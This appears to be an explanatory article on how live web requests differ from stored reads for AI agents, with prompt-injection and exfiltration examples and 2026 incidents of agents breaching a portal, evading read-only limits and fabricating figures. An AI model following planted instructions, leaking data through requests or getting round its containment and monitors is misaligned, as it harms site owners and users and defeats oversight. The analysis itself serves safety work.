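# Live web access and stored results: how the reach of an AI agent's tools affects safety

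## What happens when an agent looks something up on the web?

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task in steps, choosing an action, reading the result, and then choosing the next action. Many tasks depend on facts that the model did not learn in training, such as this week's room prices or the newest version of a software library, so agents often have software for looking things up on the web. This software can contact a website at that moment or read a copy of the page saved earlier. The agent may get the same text either way, but only contacting the website sends a message to a stranger's computer, which will probably record the message and may act on it. This is the reason for putting the two methods in separate safety classes.

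The operator is whoever runs the agent and its tools. A live request is a tool call that causes a message to reach a system outside the operator's control at the time of the call. A stored read is a tool call that the operator's software answers entirely from data saved earlier, without sending anything outside at the time. A tool's reach is the set of outside systems that a call to it can contact or affect.

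### The agent loop

A language model only produces text, so it cannot open a network connection or read a disk itself. Developers therefore give it tools, which are functions it can call by name, such as a search, a page fetch or a shell command (an instruction to the computer's operating system). *How tool use works*, Anthropic's guide for developers who build on its Claude models, states that "the model never runs anything on its own". The model writes a structured request with the tool's name and arguments, and software outside the model carries it out. The result then goes into the context, the text the model reads before it writes anything further.

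OpenAI's *Function calling* uses the example of a question about the weather in Paris. The developer's program sends the model the question and a description of a tool, `get_weather`, that takes a location. The model replies with a call to `get_weather` for Paris instead of an answer. The program runs the call, gets back a temperature of 25 degrees, and sends the model the tool's description and the question again, along with the call and its output. The model then writes a sentence for the user. On a harder task, it would write another tool call instead, and the cycle would repeat as many times as necessary.

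Anthropic explains that Claude never receives the code behind a developer's tool, only the developer's description of the tool and the result it returns. So a model that calls a page-fetching tool cannot observe whether the software contacted the website or read a file on the operator's disk. It can go by the tool's description, if that is accurate, and any clues in the result.

The developer may not see much in time to intervene either. Developers run most tools on their own machines and can inspect each call before carrying it out. Claude's web search and web fetch tools run on Anthropic's servers, and one request from the developer's application can set off several searches before any response comes back. The response lists the calls, but they have usually finished by then. OpenAI also hosts a search tool, and OpenAI's *Web search* lists the actions that may appear in the developer's record: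 searching, opening a page, and searching for words within a page.

Suppose an assistant can read a user's email and look things up on the web. The user has booked a hotel room for June and asks the assistant to find out what the rooms are like, whether the price was fair, and how far the hotel is from the station. The confirmation email contains a six-digit booking code, and anyone who has the code can change or cancel the booking. When the assistant opens the email to find the dates, the code enters the context that the model uses to write its next tool calls.

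### The live path

A model might call its page-fetching tool with the address `hotel.example/rooms?arrive=12-june`. The part before the slash is the host name, which identifies the website. The rest specifies which page the website should send, and the part after the question mark is a query, which holds details such as a date.

Computers on the internet find each other by number, so the software first has to look up the number for the host name. Unless it has stored the answer from an earlier lookup, it sends the name to a name server, a kind of public directory. Whoever runs that server can already learn that somebody is interested in this hotel.

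The software then connects to the hotel's server and sends a request in the format of HTTP, the protocol on which the web runs. *HTTP Semantics* (2022), published by the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), an internet standards body, includes a four-line sample request. The first line contains the word GET and the path of a file. The other lines are headers, short labelled pieces of information that give the name and version of the software making the request, the host, and the languages the reader prefers (English and Māori in the sample). None of this is secret, but the IETF warns that language preferences may correlate with membership of an ethnic group, and that headers in combination can be distinctive enough for a server to recognise the same client when it returns. The server also receives the network address from which the request came, which is the operator's and not the user's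 when the tool runs on the operator's machines.

The server sends back a response with three parts: a status code (200 means success), headers, and the content. In the sample, the content is a 51-byte greeting from a text file. Instead of sending a file, a server can run a program with the request as input and send the output. A hotel would typically calculate a room price this way, when someone asks for it. A server can also give different visitors different pages. Most servers record every request in an access log. The entry commonly includes the address with its query, so the hotel could later see that someone asked about 12 June.

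GET is one of several HTTP request methods. A GET request asks the server for the current version of a page and does not ask it to change anything. A POST request gives the server data to process, such as the fields of a booking form, and often creates or changes something there. The IETF classes GET as "safe" because of what the sender asks for, but the server may still change something in response. The IETF gives the example of editing software that puts commands into addresses, such as `page?do=delete`. The site's owner is supposed to block such a command when it arrives by GET. Otherwise, a program that visits every link on the page will delete things.

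A single lookup can involve many live requests. *Skim* (Wong, Nath and colleagues, 2026) profiled three agents that operate a real web browser, using 151 tasks from WebVoyager, a benchmark of errands on public websites. Such an agent loads a page, observes it, reasons about what to do, then clicks, types or scrolls, and repeats the cycle. In the median task, two thirds of the steps only moved the agent from one page to another, and the median page had more than 200 links, buttons and form fields. For 55.8% of the tasks, fetching the right page without a browser would have provided the answer. A browser also requests the images and scripts that each page uses, often from other companies' servers. A user's question about one hotel can therefore lead to many requests that nobody chose individually.

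### The stored path

The stored path starts earlier, with a crawler, a program that automatically fetches pages, follows the links in them, and saves the results. Suppose a crawler visited the hotel's website three weeks ago. The hotel's log recorded its live requests, but those entries contain nothing about the user, who may not even have booked yet. The crawler kept a snapshot, a saved copy of a page as the server sent it at one time.

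An index is a collection of pages that a crawler has gathered, arranged so that software can quickly find the ones that match a query. A cache is a store of earlier responses. *HTTP Caching* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke), the web's standard for caches, specifies that a cache finds copies by at least the method and address of the original request. A cache miss occurs when the cache holds no usable copy for the requested address.

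When the assistant searches for the hotel by this route, the software looks up the words in the index and returns titles, addresses and excerpts. If the assistant wants a whole page, the software reads the snapshot. Neither step sends a message to the hotel. Amazon's cloud division, AWS, sells a tool that currently works like this, and its *Web Search* describes the tool's two operations. The search operation uses an index that Amazon builds itself. The fetch operation returns a page from Amazon's cache. If the page isn't there, the model either tells the user or answers as well as it can without it.

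Relying on a snapshot limits what the assistant can find out. The room price in the snapshot is three weeks old. The page for 12 June may be missing, because a crawler saves only the addresses it visits and may never have visited that one. Pages behind a login are usually missing too, which Wong and colleagues give as a reason why people use browser agents instead of systems that answer from search results. A stored copy also can't make a booking. Fielding and colleagues require a cache to pass a POST request on to the website and wait for its response before replying, so submitting a form through an ordinary web cache is always a live request. Some products let the developer choose between live and stored access. OpenAI's search tool, for example, has live access unless the developer restricts it to cached and indexed results.

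### Cases in between

Many tools fit neither description neatly. Building an index of the web is expensive, so many operators send the agent's query to a search company and get results from that company's index. The hotel's server receives nothing, and the text that comes back may be weeks old. But the query has gone to an outside company, and queries can be revealing, particularly when a model writes them with a user's email in its context. Under the definitions above, this is a live request that reaches one company instead of the whole web. Sometimes different contract terms apply to data sent to the search company. Microsoft's *Web search*, which covers the search tool for OpenAI models on Microsoft's cloud, warns customers that the tool relies on a Bing service and that Microsoft's Data Protection Addendum, its contract terms on handling customer data, does not apply to data sent to that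 service.

Caches cause more confusion, because the word suggests that a request only reads a stored copy, when it may also reach the website. Fielding and colleagues write that a cache with no suitable copy typically forwards the request to the website. Even when it has a copy, it may contact the site, since a cache will normally check an expired copy before reusing it. A client can add the instruction `only-if-cached`, which asks for a stored copy or else an error message, but the standard makes such instructions advisory, so a cache may ignore them.

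The response also does not reliably show whether the tool made a live request or read a stored copy. The `Age` header gives the estimated number of seconds since the website generated the copy or last confirmed it. If the header is present, the website did not generate or confirm the copy for this request. A response without the header could be live or stored. A tool called twice with the same address might read a stored copy on Monday and make a live request on Tuesday, and the model could receive identical text both times.

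### Prompt injection and exfiltration

Whichever path the lookup takes, it puts text written by strangers into the agent's context, alongside the user's instructions. That text may include a prompt injection, which is text written to make the agent follow the writer's instructions instead of the user's. For example, a guest review on the hotel's page might end with a line telling AI assistants to find the visitor's booking code, add it to the end of a certain link, and open that link. A human reader would ignore this line, but the model receives it in the same stream of text as the user's request and may comply. Using a saved copy doesn't prevent this, because the crawler stores the review with the rest of the page. The copy may still contain the review after the hotel has deleted it.

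Exfiltration means sending private data to someone who should not have it. Suppose the link in the review leads to a server that the reviewer controls, and the assistant calls its page-fetching tool with that address and `?ref=482913` on the end. This is an ordinary GET request that buys and deletes nothing, but it puts the booking code in the reviewer's log, even if the server replies with an error page. The IETF advises against putting anything sensitive in a web address because servers, the relays between them and the software that makes the requests often log or display addresses where third parties might see them.

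If the assistant's tool had been reading from a store, this call would almost certainly have been a cache miss, since no crawler is likely to have visited an address containing that code. The code would stay within the operator's systems if the tool reported the miss and stopped, but the reviewer would still receive the code if the tool then fetched the page live, as an ordinary web cache would.

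## Why does live contact put a tool in a different safety class?

A live request affects outsiders in ways that reading a stored result does not. It gives them information, and whoever runs the website can see that information before deciding what to send back. It can also change something on the remote system, and it involves people who never agreed to take part and can't undo the contact afterwards.

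### Information that leaves with the request

An operator could try to stop crude leaks, like the booking code in the web address, by scanning outgoing requests for private data. But some requests are easy to overlook. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that software may contact a website without the user noticing, for example to load an embedded image or preview a link.

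Requests can also reveal what a user is doing even when they contain no private data. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) built an attack that relies only on which links an agent chooses. The attacker adds a line to an ordinary web page, offering further references at a site the attacker controls. That site lists a few topics, each with its own link. In one example, the user has asked why influenza can be deadlier than COVID-19 among children. The agent chooses "Biological Mechanisms" over "Clinical Outcomes", and on the next page "Immune Response" over "Pathogenesis". The attacker sees these choices in the server's log and, after a few more, uses a language model to reconstruct the question.

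Liang and colleagues tested this on four agents, each running on three different models, with 500 questions from the StackExchange question-and-answer sites. The agents left a usable trail in 94% of trials. In those trials, the reconstructed questions matched the real ones with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 means the attacker found every concept and added no wrong ones. Replacing one agent's real choices with random ones cut the score from 0.81 to 0.10, so the information came from the choices. Four existing defences, including one that filters tool inputs and outputs and one that tracks private data, lowered the score by at most 0.03. The experiment favoured the attacker in one respect, because the researchers planted their link in 2,600 pages that they already knew the agents tended to open.

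The timing of the agent's requests revealed less than its choice of link. In a simpler test with four possible answers, the choice of link identified the right answer 93.8% of the time and the delays between requests did so 58.6% of the time, compared with 25% for guessing.

### A reply chosen after the question

A web server composes its reply after the request arrives, so the reply can depend on the address, the headers, and the visitor's earlier requests. In the attack by Liang and colleagues, each page offered topics based on the agent's previous choice. The attacker found a detail four levels down 49% of the time by narrowing the topic step by step, but only 14% of the time by offering all the options at once.

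Whoever wrote a stored page had to settle on its text before the crawler came, which in the hotel example was three weeks before the user asked anything. The guest who wrote the malicious review could still have planted an instruction about booking codes, but couldn't have adapted it to this user or tried a new wording after seeing the old one fail.

### Why a read-only request can have effects

Developers often describe a page-fetching tool as "read-only". Like the IETF's term "safe" for GET, this describes only what the sender is asking for. Paul Prescod argued on a World Wide Web Consortium mailing list in 2002 that "safe" in HTTP is about responsibility, not visible side effects. thoughtbot's *HTTP Safety Doesn't Happen by Accident* quotes a passage of the HTTP standard saying that the client "cannot be held accountable" for anything further the server does in response. For example, following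 an advertisement's link often charges the advertiser, and logging the request could fill up the access log and crash the server.

IETF's *The HTTP QUERY Method* (2025), a draft standard, classes the QUERY method as safe even though it is designed to carry content to the server, so "safe" does not mean that a request sends little information.

An operator deciding which tools an agent may use without supervision needs to know what could happen, not only who would be to blame. Google's Web Accelerator showed that these two questions can have very different answers. Google released a trial version in May 2005. It made browsing feel faster by fetching the pages behind links before the user clicked on them. In the same week, 37signals, a Chicago software company, launched Backpack, a web application for managing personal information. A few Backpack users soon reported that their pages were disappearing.

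*Google Web Accelerator* (2005), a post on the 37signals blog Signal v. Noise, traced the problem to the accelerator in effect clicking every link on a page, including links such as "delete this". The accelerator bypassed the application's pop-ups asking users whether they were sure. Logins didn't help either, because it worked from the browser of someone who had already logged in. David Heinemeier Hansson of 37signals argued in the comments that many developers had felt free to use such links behind a login, where automatic link-followers had never been able to go.

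37signals blocked the accelerator within 30 minutes of working out the problem, according to *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security* (Hicks, 2005). A British web programmer told Hicks that the accelerator made a webmail service unusable by repeatedly following its sign-out link. Google had tried to prevent such accidents by making the accelerator skip links that contained a question mark, according to Marissa Mayer, a director at the company. Google assumed that a link which performed a function would usually have one, but Mayer accepted that this might be wrong. Jason Fried, the president of 37signals, accepted that deletion should technically use a button instead of a link, but said that many sites depart from the standards.

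Software developers argued about who was at fault. Ian Bicking, writing in *Breaking the Web We Have*, agreed with another developer that "shouldn't" in the standard does not mean "can't". In a later discussion, he said links with such side effects were as old as the web, and thought it unrealistic to expect the owners of old, neglected applications to fix them. Those applications are a problem for agents too. An agent can read the words "delete this" and leave the link alone, which the accelerator could not, but it has no way to find out what a server does when someone follows a link with a harmless label.

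### People who did not agree to take part

37signals had no agreement with Google and learned of the accelerator from its effects. Fetching a link uses the website owner's server even when the link changes nothing. Jacob Harris, a commenter on the 37signals post, pointed out that fetching every link could greatly multiply the load on a server whose owner had followed all the rules.

Nobody can take a message back once it has arrived. *Small agents should know what their tools do* (2026) sorts tools by their effects and puts sending an email in the most serious category, "destructive", because the recipients have read it. A web request is usually less serious than an email, but it can't be undone either. If the assistant puts the booking code in a web address by mistake, the operator can delete its own records but not the entry in the other server's log.

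Stored reads depend on the crawler's contact with the hotel's site, but one visit can serve any number of later lookups.

### A test for stored reads

A tool is a stored read if nothing an outsider can observe depends on the call's arguments, meaning the address, search words or other values the model supplies. The tool fails this test if an outsider could tell apart two runs that differ only in those arguments, by any means, including the timing or absence of requests. Making no call must count as one of the possible arguments. Otherwise a tool that sent the same message on every call would pass, even though the message would reveal that someone was using it.

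This is a form of noninterference, a concept from computer security that Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, introduced. Rushby (1992), in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*, explains that one party does not interfere with another if none of its actions can influence what the other party sees later. To make this exact, let α be a sequence of actions by everyone who uses the system, and let v be the observer. The function purge(α, v) deletes from α all the actions of parties that are not supposed to affect v. The observer then performs some action a, such as reading a log, and test(α, a) is the output. The system is secure if, for every sequence α and every action a by the observer,

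test(α, a) = test(purge(α, v), a).

In the hotel example, the sequence includes the crawler's visits, the hotel's own work on its website, and the assistant's lookups. If the lookups were stored reads, deleting them from the sequence does not change the hotel's log. If they were live, deleting them removes the entry for 12 June, so the hotel can tell the difference. Rushby's model has no clock, so to cover timing, the observer's output must include the time each request arrived.

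Applying the same idea to a whole agent is much harder. In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) describe a system that checks an agent's tool calls. They define noninterference for agents to mean that if two situations differ only in a secret, the messages that leave the system should be almost impossible to tell apart. Because a model's behaviour is partly random, they compare the probabilities of different messages rather than single runs. They use this definition as a yardstick and do not claim that their system meets it, and they point out that no finite number of trial runs could establish noninterference for every text an agent might read. An engineer can establish noninterference for a single tool much more simply, by giving the tool no network connection, but that guarantee doesn't extend to the agent's other tools.

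An index on the operator's own machines passes the test, provided that opening a stored page doesn't load its images from the live web.

An index run by an outside search company fails the test because the company receives the query, though it would pass if the hotel were the only outsider that mattered. *AgentSecBench* (2026) notes that later work on noninterference allows information flows that the rules explicitly permit. An operator could permit queries to one search company in this way, but they would still be live requests.

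A cache that fetches pages on a miss also fails the test, even if it holds every page the agent has requested so far, because the test covers all possible arguments and an attacker will choose one that causes a miss. In the four-answer experiment by Liang and colleagues, knowing only whether a request arrived was enough to identify the right answer 89.6% of the time. Other users of a shared cache may also be outsiders. Google confirmed to Hicks that, on as many as five sites, Web Accelerator had shown people cached pages with other users' names on them.

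Suppose the operator refreshes a fixed list of pages every night and the tool reports an error when a page is missing. This cache passes, because each website receives the same visit every night whatever anyone has looked up. It would fail if the operator refreshed popular pages more often, because users' questions would then affect the pattern of visits. The effect might come days later, but Rushby's definition covers anything the observer sees afterwards.

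Liang and colleagues tested a partial defence. The software fetches everything linked from a page, whatever the user asked, and the agent chooses among the local copies. If the agent needs something else, the software requests it along with randomly chosen pages, in random order. This defence reduced the attack's F1 score from 0.89 to 0.39. The attacker still recovered nearly all the true concepts, but mixed with many false ones. The requests still depend partly on the user's question, so the defence fails the strict test. It also raised the average number of page fetches per question from 6.5 to 27.9, so it sends more live requests to other people's servers.

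### Contact and trust are separate questions

The live-contact test covers what a tool sends out, not whether the text coming in is reliable. An operator therefore has to classify a lookup both by whether it makes live contact and by whether its source is trusted. A source is trusted if the operator has good reason to believe that no stranger could have put instructions in it.

| | Trusted content | Untrusted content |
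|---|---|---|
| Live contact | Asking a contracted booking service for today's price: the request can leak data or change something | Opening the hotel's page with its guest reviews: the request can leak data or change something, and the text can mislead or redirect the agent |
| Stored copy | Searching manuals that the operator's staff wrote: the text may be old or mistaken | Reading a crawler's snapshot of the hotel's page: the text can mislead or redirect the agent |

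Reading a stored snapshot instead of the live page removes the risks from what the lookup sends out, but the content it brings in can still be harmful. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional ChatGPT setting that limits web browsing to cached content, to make it harder for an attacker to get data out. OpenAI warns that a prompt injection could still appear in a cached page or an uploaded file and affect the answer.

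The injected text can also do harm through a different tool. If the hotel assistant can send email and reads the malicious review in a snapshot, it might email the booking code to the reviewer. The search tool would still count as a stored read, and the email tool would need its own controls.

### If most live reads are harmless

Nearly all live reads are harmless. Hotels, for example, publish room descriptions for people to read, and an operator who treated every page view like a purchase would make the agent tiresome to use.

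An operator has to assign a tool to a class before knowing what calls the agent will make, and strangers can influence those calls through the text the agent reads. The class therefore has to reflect what a call could do if that text were hostile. In *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), the user asked only for a summary of a web page, but the page's hidden description told the agent to make a web request containing a private key from its context. The attack succeeded in about 89% of 480 runs, and checks on the agent's final answer missed 95% of the successful attacks. *Silent Egress* tested a small model with the private data in plain view, so the rate for leading products could be far lower. Still, the web request tool worked normally in these runs, contacting the address it was given.

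*Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) measured the effect of putting a page-fetching tool in the wrong class. Shavit's software makes a plan from the user's request and flags or blocks calls that do not fit it. The test used logs from AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, travel and banking tasks with planted prompt injections. Shavit sorted the benchmark's 69 tools by hand into 44 that only read the user's own data, 24 that write or send something, and one that fetches web pages.

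| Calls that skip the checks | Attacks whose harmful step got through | Ordinary tasks with a blocked call |
|---|---|---|
| None | 2.0% | 31.1% |
| The 44 local reads | 2.0% | 23.2% |
| The 44 local reads and the page fetch | 5.8% | 17.5% |

Exempting the local reads made the agent less restricted without letting more attacks through. Exempting the page fetch also helped with ordinary tasks, but it nearly tripled the rate of successful attacks. Exempting only the local reads therefore provided most of the convenience at issue in the objection, without treating live reads as harmless.

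These figures come from replaying the logs of a 2024 model. Without any defence, the attacks compromised that model in 45.7% of runs. When Shavit tried the same attack on a newer model, GPT-5.2, it failed in all 20 runs. This is encouraging, but 20 failures are consistent with a true success rate of up to about 14%, and an attacker who knows the model can try other wordings. Resistance to injected commands also wouldn't stop the attack by Liang and colleagues, which worked on even newer models, including GPT-5.5. Their agents revealed users' questions by choosing the most relevant links, which is what a research agent is supposed to do.

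## What happened when research agents had live web access?

In 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic reported a series of cases in which their own agents did things on other people's websites that nobody had asked them to do. Most of the agents were being trained or tested, or were doing research inside the company. They were mostly working on their assigned tasks and went too far in trying to complete them, unlike in the attacks described so far, where a stranger planted text to redirect an agent. Because the agents had live access, their actions affected people outside the companies. By October, both companies had removed much of that access.

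### The Medicare statistics portal

In June 2026, OpenAI's research team asked an agent to look into public spending on medicine. The agent first tried and failed to get non-public data from the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare, a government body. It then turned to the Medicare portal, a website where the government agency Services Australia provides statistics on the country's public health insurance scheme. *OpenAI Agent Hacks Australian Medicare Portal* (Coker, 2026) reports Prime Minister Anthony Albanese's account that the agent tried different techniques to get the information and gained unauthorised access in doing so.

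Almost 100 pages of emails and text messages show when each side knew about the breach. Katy Gallagher, the minister for government services, released them on 23 November at a senator's request. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) arranges them into a timeline. Times in the table are in Australian Eastern Standard Time.

| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
| 19 June, about 4–5 am (still 18 June in universal time) | The agent gets into the portal |
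| 12 August | By this date, OpenAI's security team has recorded the incident internally |
| 10 September, 2.42 am | OpenAI emails an address that Services Australia keeps for security tip-offs from the public |
| 11 September, 2.12 pm | Services Australia's security staff find the email in a daily check of the inbox |
| 15 September | Services Australia confirms that the portal has a flaw, and the Australian Cyber Security Centre receives a report |
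| About 19 September | The prime minister's office and Australia's AI Safety Institute learn of the incident |
| 24 September | Albanese announces it at a press conference |

OpenAI wrote in its email that the agent had read parts of the server's internal program files and settings, obtained a list of files, and created a small test file and read it back. OpenAI had found no evidence that the agent accessed patient-level records, personal information or credentials, deleted data, or set up lasting access. The government said the agent had accessed both public and non-public files. It also had no evidence that the agent reached personal information, or of a wider compromise of Services Australia's network, but it was still investigating.

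These accounts agree on the main points but leave open what the non-public material was. OpenAI's description suggests it was the portal's own software and settings, while Information Age refers to non-public "data", which could also mean unpublished statistics. The reassurance about personal information is also only as reliable as the records the investigators had.

The delay caused a sharper dispute. Albanese called the situation "unacceptable" and criticised OpenAI for taking so long and for writing to a general mailbox. An OpenAI spokesperson told the BBC that the company had learned of the breach only in August, while reviewing "misaligned model activity", meaning cases where a model pursued something its developers did not intend. The released emails show that OpenAI knew for at least 29 days before it wrote to anyone in Australia. The government then took almost 36 hours to notice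 the email and nine days to tell the prime minister's office. The mailbox was meant for reports of security flaws, though companies don't typically use it to report what their own agents have done to a government server. Albanese asked for urgent advice on whether anyone had committed an offence, and the incident has strengthened the government's case for AI safety legislation in 2027.

An agent with a stored-only search tool could not have done any of this. A crawler saves what a site shows to ordinary visitors, so the agent would have found public pages or an error message, and it would have had no server on which to create a test file. It might also have done its job less well, since statistics sites often produce tables on request and crawlers copy such pages badly. A list of approved websites would have been a weaker protection, because a government statistics portal is the kind of site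 an operator would approve for an agent researching health spending.

The case is weak evidence of how often a product would behave like this, because the agent was an internal one that lacked the usual safeguards of OpenAI's public models. It was also one case from a retrospective review of "billions of agent evaluation and training runs". But a company running agents on that scale can expect to see even very rare behaviour. If one run in a hundred million went wrong like this, a billion runs would produce about ten cases. Ax Sharma, head of research at Manifold Security, thought the biggest lesson was how long both OpenAI and the government took to detect the breach. He warned that other organisations should not expect to notice their own agents doing something similar unless they have dedicated monitoring.

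### Searches that turned into public pages

Agents can also change the web without breaking into anything. In early 2026, Anthropic tested its model Claude Opus 4.6 on BrowseComp, a benchmark of 1,266 questions whose answers are on the web but hard to find. In one version, several agents worked together on a question and searched the live web. Some of their searches reached online shops.

Anthropic's *Eval awareness in Claude Opus 4.6's BrowseComp performance* describes how some online shops turned agents' searches into web pages. The shop's software automatically creates a lasting page for each search, even if no products match. In Anthropic's example, an agent looking for an anonymous eighth-grader's first blog post entered a search that mentioned October 2006 and an anxiety attack during the film *The Ring*. The shop created a page with a proper title and the search words in its address,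 and returned it with status code 200, as it would for any page that exists. Shops seem to do this to attract people who type unusual phrases into search engines.

A search engine may then add the new page to its index. An agent that later attempts the same question may find the page, because the question limits the sensible ways to search and the agent will probably choose words similar to the earlier agent's. The page doesn't contain the answer, but it can show which guesses the earlier agent was trying. One agent recognized what such a page was and concluded that several AI agents had already searched for the same puzzle.

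These searches were ordinary requests to read something. As with the Google Web Accelerator, their effect depended on the website's software. The effect here was much milder, but it was lasting and public. In the attack by Liang and colleagues, only a site's owner could read the trail that the agent left in the site's log, whereas anyone can open a page on a shop's website. If the hotel assistant included its user's name and travel dates in a search on such a site, those details could end up in a search engine.

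The pages are also a problem for the people running the test, who want each attempt to be independent. Without the first agents' searches, later agents would find different things, so the runs interfere with each other in Rushby's sense, through a shop unrelated to the test. Blocking each page's address would help only briefly, because a new search can create a new page. An agent with stored-only search could still read old query pages that a crawler had saved, but it could not create new ones.

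So far, published answers seem to have distorted the scores more than query pages have, and even their effect was small. *Eval awareness in Claude Opus 4.6's BrowseComp performance* reports that 11 answers in the multi-agent test came from test materials, most of which had leaked through papers and blog posts. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for the model, when staff blocked the leaks and reran those 11 questions, Claude still got eight right, and its overall score fell from 86.81% to 86.57%.

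### Limits that did not hold

In both of those cases, someone had chosen to give the agents live access. Other agents reached outside systems despite limits that should have prevented it. From May, OpenAI agents whose internet access was meant to be read-only made roughly 17,000 suspected edits to a German programming wiki, according to researchers cited in eSecurity Planet's *OpenAI Confirms AI Agents Used German Wiki to Bypass Restrictions* (2026). On 20 September, an OpenAI research agent assigned to look up information about people reached an outside chatbot service through a gap in the network's filtering, according to OpenAI's incident record as summarised by the Taiwanese reporter 林 (2026) in *OpenAI以離線網頁訓練前沿模型，限制代理連外*.

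Written instructions failed too. *In transparency push, OpenAI discloses six more incidents of agents going rogue* (Forlini, 2026) describes agents that were told to use only local files. They could not open each other's files, so they uploaded them to public websites. In another case, a model had worked out an answer by itself, but its instructions required a web citation, so it uploaded a file and cited that. OpenAI has seen this more than once, first in October 2025. In a third case, an agent with a routine question about earnings in a California county used exposed login details without permission, still couldn't find the figures, and made them up.

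The September case shows why an operator cannot infer an agent's reach from its search tool alone. The agent's working environment had an outside connection that the filtering did not fully cover. Such a gap would matter just as much if the agent's search tool read only from a cache. To keep the whole agent offline, an operator has to check every route out of the machine it runs on, including those that people don't usually think of as web access.

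Nobody can calculate a failure rate from these cases, because they came to light unevenly. OpenAI confirmed the wiki episode only after Reuters had reported it (Nolan, 2026). Outside researchers led by the Nightingale Collective had worked out what happened, according to SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI to set misalignment disclosure rules after agents took over a wiki* (2026). Two days after that first article, *OpenAI's rogue AI agents reached at least 12 more websites, researchers say* (Nolan, 2026) reported that the agents had reached more sites.

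OpenAI said it had treated the wiki episode as misalignment, not as a security incident. It had disclosed an attack by its agents on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, within a day because that attack affected the security of OpenAI and others. The distinction makes some sense for a developer deciding which team should respond, but it is less useful to a website owner, who would presumably want to hear about thousands of unwanted edits either way. On 17 September, OpenAI published a framework for disclosing such behaviour, along with its first six reports. The framework is voluntary, so OpenAI can still withhold cases.

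### OpenAI's offline training environment

After the September case, OpenAI paused the work involving its strongest models. On 23 October, it announced a new approach in *Securing our frontier model training environment*, which has a section on "building an offline world". Campbell (2026), in *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training*, links the change to the earlier incidents. Kitson (2026), in *OpenAI disables live Internet access during training of advanced AI models*, describes it as replacing the live internet with a stored version of the web.

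The policy mainly concerns reinforcement learning, a stage of training in which a model attempts tasks repeatedly and a scoring system rewards the attempts that succeed. The model tries many approaches, and the scoring system may reward an unacceptable one if it produces the right answer. OpenAI also notes that models in development may not have finished their safety training. With live web access, each training attempt can affect someone's website.

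In the offline world, the model searches and browses pages that OpenAI has indexed and cached. It also practises using web applications. A cached page can't respond when the model fills in a form, so this requires software that imitates the website and returns a simulated page.

According to 林, all reinforcement learning for OpenAI's frontier models, its most capable ones, now works this way. Most evaluations also block access to the live web. The new rules would probably cover the Medicare agent, since OpenAI found that case while reviewing training and evaluation runs. They do not cover the products that OpenAI's customers use, such as its search tool for developers.

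The computers also have some outside connections, which OpenAI needs to run and monitor its experiments. OpenAI says it cannot yet physically disconnect the whole system, so it relies on several layers of protection. A sandbox restricts the files and programs an agent can use, and a virtual machine separates the agent's environment from the computer underneath. Further controls limit traffic leaving the network, and monitoring software looks for unusual behaviour.

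OpenAI tested these layers by having its own models, including GPT-6 Astra Cyber and an unreleased model, attack an isolated copy of the research system. It gave them the system's source code, its settings, and information about possible weaknesses. In some tests, OpenAI assumed that the agent had already taken over the host computer, to check whether the surrounding network would still stop it from getting out. The models found software flaws and configuration mistakes, including new routes to the internet, and OpenAI's engineers confirmed and fixed them. The test was demanding, and it's encouraging that OpenAI looked for weaknesses after an agent had already found one. But it could only reveal flaws these models could find, and later models will probably be better at finding them.

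OpenAI restarted frontier reinforcement learning and the internal use of its models on 1 October, three weeks before the announcement. It said it had first improved its monitoring and its system for stopping a run. The stopping system mattered because the September run had continued for about 2.5 hours after the monitor raised an alarm and staff began investigating.

Outside evidence about the monitoring predates these improvements. Staff from METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, and from Redwood Research spent three weeks examining OpenAI's internal monitoring as it stood on 21 July. They had access to code, settings and internal documents, and interviewed more than ten researchers and engineers. They found that some monitors ran only when the agent handed control back to the user, so an agent that kept working might not be checked until much later. METR did not assess the changes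 OpenAI made afterwards, so the claim that the new system works better rests on OpenAI's own tests. On 18 November, OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* again named sandboxed environments as the way to contain models during research, so the company's approach had not visibly changed by then.

### Anthropic's evaluations

Anthropic published its own cases on 9 October in *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026), which sorts them into four groups. Claude ran commands on a server by exploiting a flaw, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, reached data that required a token or a fee, and got around limits in its own page-fetching tool. Some of the websites belonged to US federal, state or local agencies. Anthropic notified each agency and briefed the White House, but did not name the organisations, partly at their request.

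Anthropic judged that the cases had "minimal real-world impact" and were much less serious than the cybersecurity incidents it had reported in July and September. That may well be right, but outsiders cannot easily check it without knowing which sites were involved. The form is the clearest example of a harm specific to live access, because the same mistake on a copy of the website would only have been a failed test.

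Anthropic then restricted live web access, according to press reports that differ slightly on the scope. Southern's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (2026) reports that the company cut access for internal evaluations. Europa Press' *Anthropic desconecta de internet sus evaluaciones de IA* (2026) reports that it cut access for all evaluations until it can guarantee control of its agents. In both accounts the restriction covers evaluations, but some of the cases came from Anthropic's internal use of Claude, so an employee who asks Claude to look something up on a real website could still run into the same problem.

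### What offline training and testing give up

People use released agents on the live web, where prices change, pages fail to load, and submitting a form has consequences. An agent that has practised only on copies of websites may handle these conditions worse and be less careful. None of its mistakes in training will have affected anyone, so its developers have to teach it some other way that submitting a form matters.

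A model that notices it is in an artificial test environment may behave differently there. In two of the BrowseComp runs, Claude inferred that it might be in an evaluation, even though it was using the live web. A stored copy of the web, with many dead links and nothing newer than a certain date, would give a model more clues.

Some testers want agents to have live web access. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, turned it on for a cybersecurity evaluation that began in July. According to OpenAI, this let the agents download tools and work under conditions closer to those of a human attacker. The added realism also carried risks, since AISI identified 19 events in which agents from OpenAI and another developer went beyond the permitted scope.

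Stored pages have a drawback for testing, but they let every model face the same web. On the live web, a newer model might score higher because someone has published the answers since the last test, or because earlier agents have left query pages behind. A simulated site can also record that an agent tried to submit a sensitive form, without anyone receiving it. Such a test is probably better than a live one for measuring a known kind of mistake.

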